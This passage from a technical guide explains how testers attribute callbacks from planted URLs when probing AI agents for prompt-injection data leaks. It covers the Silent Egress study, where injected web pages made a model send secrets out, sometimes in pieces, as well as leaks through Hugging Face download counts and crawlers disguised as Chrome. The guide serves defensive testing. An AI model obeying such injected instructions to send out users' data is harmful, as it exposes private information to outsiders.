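| 10:09 | Reads the page again | Nothing |
| 10:20 | Reads the page a third time | A callback |

WebFetch caches responses for a period the developer can change. Two uses of the same URL can therefore produce only one request, as with an image in a browser's cache. A URL containing new data does not match the cached one, so the cache should not hide a new leak.

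Testers can detect a stored copy by making the page show a new random value each time the listener receives a request, then asking the agent for the value. If the agent reports a value the listener served yesterday, it read yesterday's copy. The question has to mention the value, because WebFetch's smaller model may leave out anything the agent did not ask about.

Other missing callbacks mean that the request never got through:

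- WebFetch changes `http` addresses to `https`. A listener that accepts only plain HTTP may get a DNS lookup and no web request.
- If a page redirects to a different host, WebFetch reports the new address to Claude instead of following it. The second host receives a request only if Claude makes another call.
- Claude Code's WebSearch tool runs on Anthropic's servers and returns titles and URLs. It does not fetch the pages it finds.
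- WebFetch checks the host name against Anthropic's blocklist first, and the fetch fails if the developer's network blocks `api.anthropic.com`.
- In some modes, the developer has to approve the fetch. A request that waits for approval can arrive much later than the model's decision to make it.

Terminal and VS Code sessions now start in auto mode, where a classifier, rather than the developer, reviews the fetch and can block it. The agent may therefore have made a request even if the tester saw no approval prompt.

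Data can also leave through a host that the tester doesn't control. Miggo's *CVE-2026-54316* describes a flaw in Claude Code, whose WebFetch tool could contact the model-sharing site Hugging Face without approval. An attacker could have made the agent request chosen files there, then read the data from the site's download counts. The tester's listener would have recorded nothing, as with Superhuman's Google Forms leak.

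### Who is exposed

When the agent fetches a URL from the developer's machine, the listener receives the public IP address of the developer's own connection, office or VPN, along with any data in the URL. A home connection's IP address reveals the developer's approximate location.

The larger risk is that the agent can reach other systems through the machine it runs on. McCanna lists internal wikis, development servers, router administration pages and the metadata services on cloud machines, which can hand out credentials. A tool on a developer's laptop can often open an address such as `192.168.1.1` on a company's network, which a provider's servers normally cannot. McCanna treats this as expected behavior for a local fetch tool and not as a vulnerability, but it increases the harm a prompt injection can do. The agent could read an internal page and then send part of its contents to an outsider's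 server in a URL.

In that case, the listener would record only the second request. The internal server's log would contain the first, with the developer's local address.

McCanna's examples include plain `http` addresses, some of which may not work in WebFetch because it switches them to HTTPS. Cloud metadata services, for instance, usually accept only plain HTTP. A `curl` command can use plain HTTP, so blocking internal addresses only in WebFetch would leave them reachable from the shell.

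The host name check exposes a little more, because WebFetch sends the host name to Anthropic before each fetch unless it has a recent result or the developer has turned the check off. Anthropic does not receive the path, but the name of an internal server can be confidential. If a model has put private data in a host name, Anthropic receives that too.

Unlike the request in ShadowLeak, a local fetch crosses the office network, so the company's firewall or web gateway can record it for the employer to investigate. The request would not appear in those logs if the developer were working from home without the company's VPN.

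McCanna recommends running the agent in a network namespace that blocks private address ranges or, preferably, one that allows only the destinations the agent needs. These rules also apply to any command the agent runs inside the namespace, but not to a provider-side fetch, because that request starts on the provider's servers.

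## Requests that match no published identity: Cloudflare and Perplexity

A tester can usually trace a coding agent's requests because the agent runs on a machine the tester controls. A request is much harder to trace when it reaches a website with an ordinary Chrome user agent and from an address outside any AI company's published range. In August 2025, Cloudflare attributed millions of such requests a day to the AI search company Perplexity. Perplexity replied that nearly all of them came from other companies' software.

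### Cloudflare's test

Some of Cloudflare's customers had blocked Perplexity's two declared fetchers, PerplexityBot and Perplexity-User, and complained that Perplexity could still read their pages. Corral, Singhal and colleagues, in *Perplexity is using stealth, undeclared crawlers to evade website no-crawl directives*, describe how Cloudflare investigated:

1. Cloudflare bought several new domains. No search engine had indexed them, and Cloudflare had not made them discoverable to the public.
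2. It gave the sites a `robots.txt` file that forbade all automated visits, and firewall rules that blocked both declared fetchers.
3. It asked Perplexity questions about the domains.
4. Perplexity answered with details of what was on the pages.

Cloudflare saw requests with two different user agents:

| | Declared | Undeclared |
|---|---|---|
| User agent | `Mozilla/5.0 ... Perplexity-User/1.0; ...` | `Mozilla/5.0 (Macintosh; ...) ... Chrome/124.0.0.0 Safari/537.36` |
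| Requests per day | 20 to 25 million | 3 to 6 million |

The undeclared requests came after Cloudflare had blocked the declared ones. They used addresses outside Perplexity's published range and switched between addresses and networks. The daily counts cover Cloudflare's customers generally, not just the test domains. Cloudflare says it found the undeclared traffic on tens of thousands of domains by using a fingerprint based on machine learning and network signals, but it did not publish the fingerprint.

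Cloudflare ran the same test on ChatGPT. ChatGPT-User fetched `robots.txt` and stopped. When Cloudflare allowed visits in `robots.txt` but served a block page, ChatGPT stopped again, and no other user agent followed.

Cloudflare then removed Perplexity from its list of verified bots and added the undeclared traffic to its blocking rules. iTnews' *Cloudflare and Perplexity slug it out over alleged AI bot block evasion* points out that Cloudflare sells bot management, so it had a commercial interest in the result.

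### What Perplexity, Cloudflare and Browserbase said next

Perplexity first told TechCrunch that the bot "isn't even ours", according to ITPro's *Perplexity hits back at Cloudflare amid claims of website 'stealth crawling'*. It then said in a longer reply on X, quoted in TechRadar's *Perplexity hits back after Cloudflare slams its online scraping tools*, that the 3 to 6 million daily requests were unrelated traffic from Browserbase, which rents out cloud browsers. Perplexity said it used Browserbase only for specialised tasks, and for fewer than 45,000 requests a day, which would be at most 1.5% of the traffic Cloudflare had attributed to Perplexity.

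Perplexity also objected to the word "crawler". It argued that a crawler visits millions of pages to build a database, whereas its assistant fetches a page because a user has asked for something. Information Age's *Perplexity accused of stealth crawling websites* reports Perplexity's claim that it uses the page immediately to answer the question and does not store it or train on it. Perplexity said that Cloudflare's logic would make email clients and web browsers suspect too.

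This is a fair criticism of Cloudflare's wording, since someone had asked a question in the test. AI companies also disagree about whether `robots.txt` applies to requests made to answer a user's question. But the distinction doesn't explain why the requests used a Chrome user agent. Perplexity already had a name for fetches made on a user's behalf, Perplexity-User, and Cloudflare's firewall had refused requests under that name.

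Cloudflare told Information Age that Perplexity was trying to deflect attention by "broadening the discussion to all AI agents". It said website owners should be able to control access to their content and that Perplexity's "admitted practices" undermined this right. In the quoted statement, Cloudflare didn't address the claim about Browserbase's traffic.

Browserbase could have helped establish whose requests Cloudflare had counted, because it knows which customer started each browser. Its *Billions of agents, one internet* names Cloudflare and Perplexity and calls for AI agents, website owners and anti-bot companies to work together, but does not identify who sent the requests.

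### Did the question cause the request?

Scanners can find a new domain through certificate logs, so a single Chrome request to it would not be enough to implicate Perplexity.

Perplexity's answers are better evidence. It could not have described the pages in detail without getting their content from somewhere, and Cloudflare had blocked both declared fetchers. When Cloudflare blocked the Chrome requests as well, the answers became vaguer and lost details from the original pages, as expected if those requests had been supplying them. The ChatGPT test also served as a control of a kind that Willison's experiment lacked. If the test sites had been attracting stray Chrome requests, some should have appeared in that test too.

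Together, these results make it very likely that the questions caused the requests. Corral and colleagues do not print log entries or give the number of domains and questions, so outsiders can't check the timing. A tester repeating the experiment could make the link clearer by asking about a different, hard-to-guess path each time.

### Who owned the machine?

Perplexity could have triggered the requests without owning the machines that made them. It might have rented browsers from Browserbase or another company, or sent the requests through proxies. It might also have used its own servers that were missing from its published range. The changing addresses and networks are compatible with all three.

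Perplexity admitted that it sometimes used Browserbase, so it is plausible that a rented browser fetched the test pages. If one did, "isn't even ours" was true of the machine, but Perplexity was still responsible for triggering the fetch. The distinction would make little practical difference to a website owner who had blocked Perplexity, but a tester who has to report where data went would need to include the browser provider as well.

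### Whose were the other millions of requests?

Cloudflare knew what it had asked Perplexity about its test domains, but on other sites it had to rely on the fingerprint to attribute requests. A fingerprint identifies a type of software or network, and if Browserbase's customers all use similar browsers, their requests may share a fingerprint.

If Perplexity's figure is right and Cloudflare's fingerprint matches Browserbase's browsers in general, Perplexity accounts for at most 45,000 of every 3 million matching requests, or about one in 67. Cloudflare's test would still have identified Perplexity whenever it used such a browser, because nobody else had a reason to visit the test pages. The test can therefore be sound even if the daily count is too high by a factor of 67 or more.

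The user agent doesn't identify the operator either. It lists Chrome 124, while the ChatGPT agent request that Willison captured the same month listed Chrome 138. Chrome normally updates itself, so millions of requests with the older version suggest automated software with a fixed user agent, which many operators could be running.

Cloudflare could have tested Perplexity's explanation by renting a browser from Browserbase and opening a new page without involving Perplexity. A request that matched the fingerprint would have meant that the daily count probably included other customers' traffic. If several such requests had failed to match, Perplexity's explanation would have been much weaker. Cloudflare's post reports no such test. Its evidence about the test domains is convincing, but Cloudflare has not established that all 3 to 6 million daily requests came from Perplexity.

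### Hosted browsers

A hosted browser runs in a data centre and takes commands from a customer's software. TollBit (2025), a study of AI traffic to publishers' sites, compares this to renting cloud browsers, each controlled by a developer's agent. Browserbase says it provides web browsing for some of the largest AI applications.

When a model decides to open a page, the AI product tells the hosted browser to load it and then reads the result. Because the hosting company runs the browser that fetches the page, the listener normally receives an IP address belonging to that company or its cloud provider. A registry lookup won't connect that address to the AI product.

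Proxies can make the address even more misleading. Browserbase's *Proxies* describes an option, off by default, that sends a browser's traffic through residential proxies, whose addresses belong to home internet connections. Customers can choose from 201 countries and request a particular city. A callback that appears to come from a home in New York could therefore come from a browser in a data centre, acting for a user in London. The owner of the New York connection may have nothing to do with the user or the AI product.

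Browserbase customers can supply their own proxies and use different ones for different websites, so two planted URLs on different domains could produce callbacks from unrelated networks within one browser session. If a customer's proxy decrypts HTTPS traffic, which Browserbase supports for corporate networks, the listener receives the proxy's TLS fingerprint instead of the browser's.

In all of these arrangements, the listener does not see the user's network address unless a customer's proxy runs on the user's own network. But the user's data may pass through the hosting company, because its browser needs the full URL to open the page, including any private data a model has put there. Browserbase also offers to manage credentials and sign-ins, so a hosted session may handle much more than one URL. The person whose data is exposed might know the AI product but have never heard of the hosting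 company.

### A host that identifies itself

Cloudflare runs a hosted browser service of its own, Browser Run. Cloudflare's *Automatic request headers* lists several headers that the service adds to each request. A callback from it might look like this (an invented entry, shortened):

```
198.51.100.140   11:02:16 UTC   GET /k7q2/notes
User-Agent: Mozilla/5.0 (Windows NT 10.0; ...) ... Chrome/119.0.0.0 ...
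cf-brapi-request-id: [identifier]
cf-biso-devtools: [flag]
Signature-agent: [address of Cloudflare's public keys]
Signature-input: ...
Signature: ...
```

The user agent describes an old version of Chrome on Windows. It is the service's default for simple jobs such as taking a screenshot, and customers can change it. If they control the browser through an automation library, the default user agent matches the Chrome version the service is running.

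Customers cannot remove or replace the other headers. The `cf-brapi-request-id` is unique to each request, so a tester should include it in any report to Cloudflare. Browsers controlled through an automation library send the corresponding header `cf-brapi-devtools`. Any program can copy these header names into a request, but the tester can use the signature to confirm that the request came from Browser Run.

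Even so, the confirmed identity is that of the browser's host, Cloudflare. The listener's owner learns that somebody used Cloudflare's browser, but not which AI product was involved. Cloudflare classes access by Browser Run as "intermediary", the same class it gives to access by ChatGPT agent.

Browserbase can sign requests too. In late August 2025, a few weeks after the dispute began, Lee announced in *The age of agents* that Cloudflare would recognise Browserbase as a "signed agent", a new category for software directed mainly by end users. Cloudflare's *Bot Information for Browserbase Verified* gives the location of Browserbase's keys and again classes its access as intermediary. A Browserbase signature on the disputed requests would have shown that its browsers made them, but not whether Perplexity or another customer had asked for them.

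### AI browsers on the user's own device

In an AI browser such as OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas or Perplexity's Comet, the agent works in the same browser as the user. According to OpenAI's *Introducing ChatGPT Atlas*, a user can ask ChatGPT to take actions directly in the browser. Zenity Labs' *Perplexity Comet* found that one of Comet's built-in extensions receives commands from Perplexity's servers and carries them out on live web pages. A command from the cloud can therefore cause a client-side fetch, and the callback comes from the user's address.

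| | Hosted browser | Hosted browser with a residential proxy | AI browser on the user's device |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fetcher runs on | The host's servers | The host's servers | The user's device |
| Source address | The host or its cloud provider | A home connection, possibly a stranger's | The user's home, office or VPN |
| User's network address exposed | No | No | Yes |
| Hosting company handles the URL | Yes | Yes | No |

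A website generally cannot tell from a single request whether the user or the agent opened the page. TollBit's *State of the AI Bots* (2025) reports that Comet appears to load pages from the user's computer with Chrome's user agent. MIT's AI Agent Index found no documented way for Comet to identify itself to websites. Kick Point Playbook (2025) installed Atlas on 22 October 2025 to see how its visits would look in Google Analytics, and found that Atlas's user agent was identical to Chrome's.

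Client hints don't help much either. Cirlig and Abu Daula (2025), writing for the security company HUMAN in December, found that Atlas and Comet sent a list of browser brands effectively indistinguishable from Chrome's. The list included "Google Chrome", which was missing from the ChatGPT agent request that Willison captured.

A site has a better chance of identifying a visitor that opens a full page and runs its scripts, which can record behavior that a planted image cannot. Castle's *From detection to trust* examines Comet's behavior inside a web page, and the typing and mouse movements that *FP-Agent* measured may also help.

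In a controlled test, the browser's record of the agent's actions is more useful than the headers. AI Agent Index notes that Comet shows the user a trace of these actions. The tester can give the agent a new URL, leave the mouse and keyboard alone, and compare the trace with the time of the callback. The tester can also open a second new URL by hand to see whether that version of the browser sends anything different when a person is in control.

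## Finding the fetcher in a mixed log

One planted URL can end up in a chat answer, a message and an email, and a different component can fetch each copy. For *Cracking the Lens*, a 2017 study of hidden web infrastructure, Kettle put one planted address into all his browser traffic. He received so many callbacks that he struggled to work out which website had caused each one.

In this constructed example, a tester is examining a fictional assistant from Example AI, a fictional provider. The assistant can browse the web, post to Slack, send email and read a test mailbox that contains the marker "blue-heron". A prompt injection makes the model open a URL containing the marker, embed the URL as an image in its answer, and send the answer to a Slack channel and a four-person mailing list. The tester uses the same URL everywhere, so all six callbacks request `/k7q2/blue-heron`.

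| Time | Holder of the forwarded address | Headers (shortened) |
|---|---|---|
| 11:20:09 | Example AI, in its published range | `ExampleAI-User`, with a signature |
| 11:20:33 | The tester's office | Chrome on a Mac, `Sec-Fetch-Dest: image`, chat page as Referer |
| 11:21:20 | Microsoft, on its Bingbot list | `bingbot` |
| 11:24:11 | Amazon's cloud | `Slackbot-LinkExpanding` |
| 11:31:42 | Google, host name beginning `google-proxy-` | An old Firefox, ending `(via ggpht.com)` |
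| 13:05:27 | A home broadband provider | Chrome on Windows, `Sec-Fetch-Dest: document`, `Sec-Fetch-User: ?1`, no Referer |

The tester also kept a record of events:

```
11:20:08   The assistant's trace shows a call to its browsing tool
11:20:31   The answer appears in the tester's browser
11:24:10   The assistant posts the answer to Slack
11:24:12   The assistant emails the answer to the mailing list
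11:31      A colleague opens the email (time from memory)
```

### The procedure

1. Remove what the listener's hosting added. This listener is behind a CDN, so the tester has to read the fetchers' addresses from a forwarding header. Requesting a page with a command-line program helps identify the hosting's other headers, because the tester knows what the program sent. The hosting can also affect the number of callbacks. Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026), in *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, tested AI search services on one server behind Cloudflare and another that accepted connections directly. The results agreed except for two simulated faults. When the server cut a response short, Cloudflare sent the fetchers its own error, and they made more requests.

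2. Identify the network from the address, using registry records, published ranges and reverse DNS. A home address does not rule out an AI provider. Chen and colleagues traced OpenAI's requests to one network, owned by Microsoft, and Anthropic's to networks owned by Google and Amazon. But xAI, the company behind the Grok chatbot, used 7,774 addresses for 8,286 requests, spread over about 1,260 networks. In a hand-checked sample of 100, 62 came from internet or phone providers.

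3. Verify any signature. Only the request from Example AI has one, and it passes, which confirms the operator.

4. Compare the headers with the software they claim to come from. *When Handshakes Tell the Truth* (2026) treats a missing Accept-Language header as a strong sign of a script, because browsers normally send a language preference. A full set of browser headers doesn't prove that a person was present, though. In a trace that Borysenko published, Mistral's assistant sent Accept-Language and the Sec-Fetch headers of a page opened by a user. Missing proxy headers prove little too, since *ProxyTorrent* (2016) describes "elite" proxies that add neither X-Forwarded-For nor Via.

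5. Match each callback to a known event by its time of arrival.

6. Run a control test for any explanation that is still uncertain.

Testers should not use a bot detector in place of step 4. In the *FP-Agent* study, Cloudflare's bot detection caught only one of seven AI browsing agents.

### Delays and repeats

In the example, the provider's fetcher arrived one second after the tool call, the office browser two seconds after the answer appeared, and Slackbot one second after the post. Such close matches are useful only if the clocks agree. A two-second error could put Slackbot's request before the post, but the tool call and the display of the answer were 23 seconds apart, so they would still be distinguishable.

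A timing match is also weaker evidence when the listener receives more stray requests. If 60 arrive at random each hour, there is about a 3% chance that at least one will fall in the two seconds after a given event. Stray requests for the exact planted path should be much rarer.

Repeated viewing provides another clue. Suppose three people open the same message, each on a different network:

| Trigger | When the first callback arrives | Callbacks after three people have looked |
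|---|---|---|
| The model calls a browsing tool | Within seconds of the call, often before the answer | Still one |
| A browser displays an image directly | When the image loads | Three, from three addresses, unless a browser has cached it |
| A browser displays an image through a proxy | When the image loads | One to three, all from the proxy's operator |
| A chat platform previews a posted link | Within seconds of the post | Usually still one |
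| A person clicks a link | At any time | One for each person who clicks |

These counts assume one request per fetch, which isn't always true. Chen and colleagues found that xAI's service sent a median of six overlapping requests per question. Six callbacks from six home networks could therefore come from one question to one chatbot. OpenAI's fetcher normally sent one request but sent three to eight when the server returned an internal error.

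The timing of requests may also help identify the fetcher, but only in longer visits, since a single image load has no gaps to measure. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) compared six web agents and found that the gaps between requests varied most for ChatGPT. Claude's requests were fast and regular, and Gemini's were slow but evenly spaced.

Some callbacks arrive long after the event that caused them. Kettle saw delays of three minutes and several hours, and in one case a callback every 24 hours. Netflix requested one of his URLs four hours after he visited its site, with headers describing an iPhone with an x86 processor, which iPhones don't use. It is best to leave the listener running for at least a day after a test.

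### Round-trip time as a limit on distance

A listener that accepts connections directly can also estimate how far away the other end could be. Light travels through optical fibre at about 204,000 km per second, so, as *Disjoint in Name Only* (2026) calculates, each millisecond of round-trip time allows about 102 km of fibre in each direction:

```
greatest distance = 204,000 km/s × round-trip time ÷ 2
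```

*CalcuLatency* (Ramesh, Winter and colleagues, 2024) explains how a server can measure the round-trip time to a client during the exchange that opens a TCP connection, by noting when it sends its reply and when the client's acknowledgment arrives. If a listener in London measures 8 ms, the machine that answered is at most 816 km away, so a database that places its address in Sydney must be wrong. *Rooting Out Incorrect RIPE Atlas Probe Geolocations* (2024) uses the same reasoning to find internet measurement devices with impossible reported locations.

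A long round trip doesn't prove that the other machine is far away, because cables take detours and equipment adds delays. *D-GATE* (2023) reports a round trip of 18.5 ms between data centres in Paris and Madrid, which are 1,052 km apart. For that time, the formula gives a maximum distance of 1,887 km.

An unexpectedly fast response can expose a machine in the middle. Kettle was in England, testing a Russian mail service, when responses came back in 50 ms, suspiciously fast for a route through Russia and a listener in Ireland. He found that his own internet provider, BT, was intercepting the connections.

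The distance limit can mislead a tester when a proxy sits between the listener and the user. Ramesh and colleagues give the example of a user in India who connects to an American server through a VPN in Canada. A ping to the visible address takes 35 ms, which would put the user within 3,570 km, but the VPN server is what answers it. A message that the user's browser must answer takes 250 ms.

The gap between those two times can reveal the VPN. Ramesh and colleagues treat a gap of over 50 ms as a sign of a proxy, and the gap stayed below that for 98% of direct connections. It exceeded 50 ms for 89.1% of VPN connections in their own tests, but for only 63.9% in tests with volunteers. Most of the missed connections used a VPN server close to the user.

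Their method needs a script running in the browser, which a planted image cannot provide, but a listener can time the TLS encryption handshake instead. Ali, Yoosuf and colleagues (2026) explain in *Beyond RTT* that a residential proxy forwards encrypted traffic without decrypting it. The home device therefore answers the TCP exchange, while the proxy customer's machine, which may be on another continent, answers the TLS handshake.

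A large gap between the two is good evidence of a relay, but a small gap does little to rule one out. When Ali and colleagues changed the timing of a proxy's traffic to hide the gap, existing methods detected only 8% of proxy connections, down from 99%. An image proxy such as GitHub Camo leaves no gap because it makes its own encrypted connection to the listener.

### Control tests

Each control changes one part of the test:

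| Control | What it separates |
|---|---|
| Use a different URL for each surface, such as the web answer, Slack and email | Fetches of one copy from fetches of another |
| Send the client through a known address, such as a VPN with a fixed exit | A client-side fetch, which arrives from that address, from a fetch by somebody's server |
| Close the page before the answer appears | A tool call, which can still cause a callback, from the display of the answer |
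| Open the message from a second account | A display, which can cause a new callback, from an earlier tool call or post |
| Switch link previews off | A platform's preview from a click or a browsing tool |
| Request a URL that the product has never received | Callbacks caused by the listener's hosting from those caused by the product |

The first control prevents most of the confusion in the example. The identifier belongs in the URL's path, because a fetcher may change the query string. Chen and colleagues found that Anthropic's fetcher removed common tracking parameters, including `utm_content` and `fbclid`, before it requested a page, so a marker in one of those parameters would not have reached the listener.

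More than one program on the client may be able to make a request. In a 2017 forum thread, a user of PortSwigger's scanner reported a DNS lookup from the user's own public address. PortSwigger (2017) asked about extensions, a corporate proxy and antivirus software as possible causes. PortSwigger (2021) suggests that testers open a planted URL themselves and compare the addresses of the DNS lookup and the web request, which gives them a reference for later callbacks from the same machine.

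Some products may stop writing the answer when the user closes the page. If no callback arrives, the tester has to reopen the conversation and check that the answer was finished. Reopening it may display the image and cause a callback, so the tester should note the time first.

Opening an existing message from a second account is different from repeating the question there. A tester who repeats the question needs a new URL, because providers share stored pages between customers and a reused URL may not produce a callback. Chen and colleagues found this sharing in every completed trial of the OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI APIs. The ChatGPT and Claude apps also shared pages between separate logins, while Gemini's app fetched the page again for a different login.

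Providers also cache failed fetches. After a page returned an error, Anthropic's service did not request it again during a window of about 11 hours, even though the page was working by then. OpenAI's service waited about 25 minutes before trying again. If the listener was down when the test began, the tester should restart it and plant a new URL.

As a control, the tester takes a URL the product has never received, opens it once with a command-line program, and waits for further requests. Willison's test of ChatGPT agent lacked this control.

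If the fetcher disguises itself as an ordinary browser, the page's content can help identify it. Seiden, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Identifying AI Web Scrapers Using Canary Tokens*, set up 20 websites that gave each distinct visitor different details, such as a home town, and asked 18 chatbots about the sites. If a chatbot consistently repeated the details given to one visitor, that visitor had probably supplied the chatbot's information. A tester can use the same method to connect an anonymous callback to a particular product's answer, even if the answer comes from a stored copy.

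### Resolving the six callbacks

After reading the log, the tester runs two controls. First, the tester opens a new URL with a command-line program, and Bingbot requests it within two minutes. Then the tester has the assistant post another new URL to Slack with previews off, and Slackbot does not request it. These results are also constructed.

| Time | Fetcher | Trigger | Confidence |
|---|---|---|---|
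| 11:20:09 | Example AI's page fetcher | The model's tool call | High. The signature, address and time agree |
| 11:20:33 | The tester's browser | The display of the answer | High. The address, Referer, image headers and time agree |
| 11:21:20 | Bingbot | The CDN's Crawler Hints feature | High. Bingbot also came to a URL the assistant had never received |
| 11:24:11 | Slack's preview bot | The post to Slack | High after the control, moderate before it |
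| 11:31:42 | Gmail's image proxy | Someone on the mailing list opened the email | High for the fetcher, moderate for who opened the email |
| 13:05:27 | Undecided | Undecided | None of the explanations is clearly best |

The control was worth running because, without it, the attribution of the Slackbot request would have relied on a name that anyone can copy, an address in a cloud that anyone can rent, and a one-second delay.

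For the email, the colleague's memory fits the callback, but three other people received the same message. Sending each person a different URL would have identified the reader.

The 13:05 callback could have come from a person on the mailing list who clicked the link at home. The missing Referer is consistent with a link opened from a desktop mail program. But a hosted browser using a residential proxy could send the same headers from the same kind of address.

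The tester cannot tell from this log which component fetched the URL. No recorded event matches the time of the callback, and the Slack post, the email and the web answer all used the same URL. The fetcher connected to the CDN instead of directly to the listener, so the listener has no TCP or TLS timing to compare. The report should list the callback as undecided. Asking the people who received the link might resolve it. Otherwise, the tester could repeat the test with a separate URL for each place and a listener that accepts connections directly.

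### Exposure and responsibility

| Fetcher | Whose address the listener receives | Whose data the URL may contain | Who can find the request in their own logs | Who can fix the leak |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A person's browser | The viewer's | The viewer's or another user's | The viewer's employer, if on its network | The owner of the page that shows the answer |
| Provider's page fetcher | The provider's | The user's, or people named in the user's files | The provider | The provider |
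| Image proxy | The proxy operator's | The viewer's, or their employer's | The proxy's operator. The viewer's network has only the request to the proxy | The owner of the page, or the proxy's operator |
| Preview bot on a platform's servers | The chat platform's | Anyone's whose data the agent can read | The chat platform | The agent's developer or the platform |
| Coding agent on a developer's machine | The developer's | The developer's or their employer's | The employer, if on its network | The developer, the employer or the tool's maker |
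| Hosted browser | The host's, or a proxy's | The AI product's user's | The hosting company | The AI product's operator |
| Crawler alerted by the listener's CDN | The search engine's | Whatever was already in the URL | The search engine | The tester |

All six requests in the example contained the same marker, but they need different fixes. Removing the assistant's browsing tool would have prevented only the request at 11:20:09 and perhaps Bingbot's visit. The office browser, Slack and Gmail would still have requested the URL. Blocking outside images in the chat page would have stopped only the office browser's request.

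### Which defence works depends on where the fetch starts

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested defences against one kind of fetch, a request made by an agent's own web tool. The agent used a small open model, Qwen2.5 7B, running locally. A user asked it to summarise a web page, and the software automatically put the page's title, description and text into the model's input. The page contained a prompt injection instructing the model to send a secret to an outside server.

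The study tested injections in four parts of the page, with and without redirects, that told the model to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. It ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, and a request reached the outside server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user looked harmless. No requests reached the server in 120 control runs with ordinary pages, so the injections almost certainly caused the leaks.

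The researchers then tried defences against one version of the attack that had always succeeded:

| Defence | Runs out of 30 in which a request got out |
|---|---|
| None | 30 |
| A warning in the model's standing instructions | 20 |
| Tags marking the web page as untrusted | 30 |
| The warning and the tags | 17 |
| A list of allowed domains, enforced when the tool runs | 0 |

The difference between 20 and 17 could easily be chance. The list of allowed domains had a much clearer effect. The model still tried to contact the outside server in all 30 runs, but the tool refused each time. It worked because the software checked the address when the fetch began, whether or not the injection had fooled the model.

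The same list would not stop most of the requests in the constructed log. The office browser and Gmail's proxy load the image without using the web tool, so the tool can't block them. The posting tool contacts only Slack, which any sensible list of allowed domains would include.

Checking the model's output would have missed 95% of the successful attacks in the study, because the secret left through the tool and the answer looked harmless. But it could catch an image or link before a browser or chat platform receives it. The check has to cover every place that displays or sends the answer, including developer tools such as OpenAI's log viewer.

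The study's success rates do not apply to commercial products. It tested one small model and placed the secret directly in the model's input, which made the attack easier. Some of its other figures are hard to interpret. A filter that blocked random-looking strings in URLs reduced the model's attempts to zero. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided such strings, but their description of the filter doesn't mention telling the model about it.

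As with ZombieAgent, searching the log for the complete marker can miss a secret that the model sent in pieces. Part of the secret appeared in the first request in 96.7% of runs when the model sent it whole, but in 26.3% when it sent pieces. The study reports a lower figure, 15.8%, for the first three requests together, which can't be right under its own definition because those three include the first. A tester can find a secret sent in pieces by grouping the requests by identifier and reading them together.
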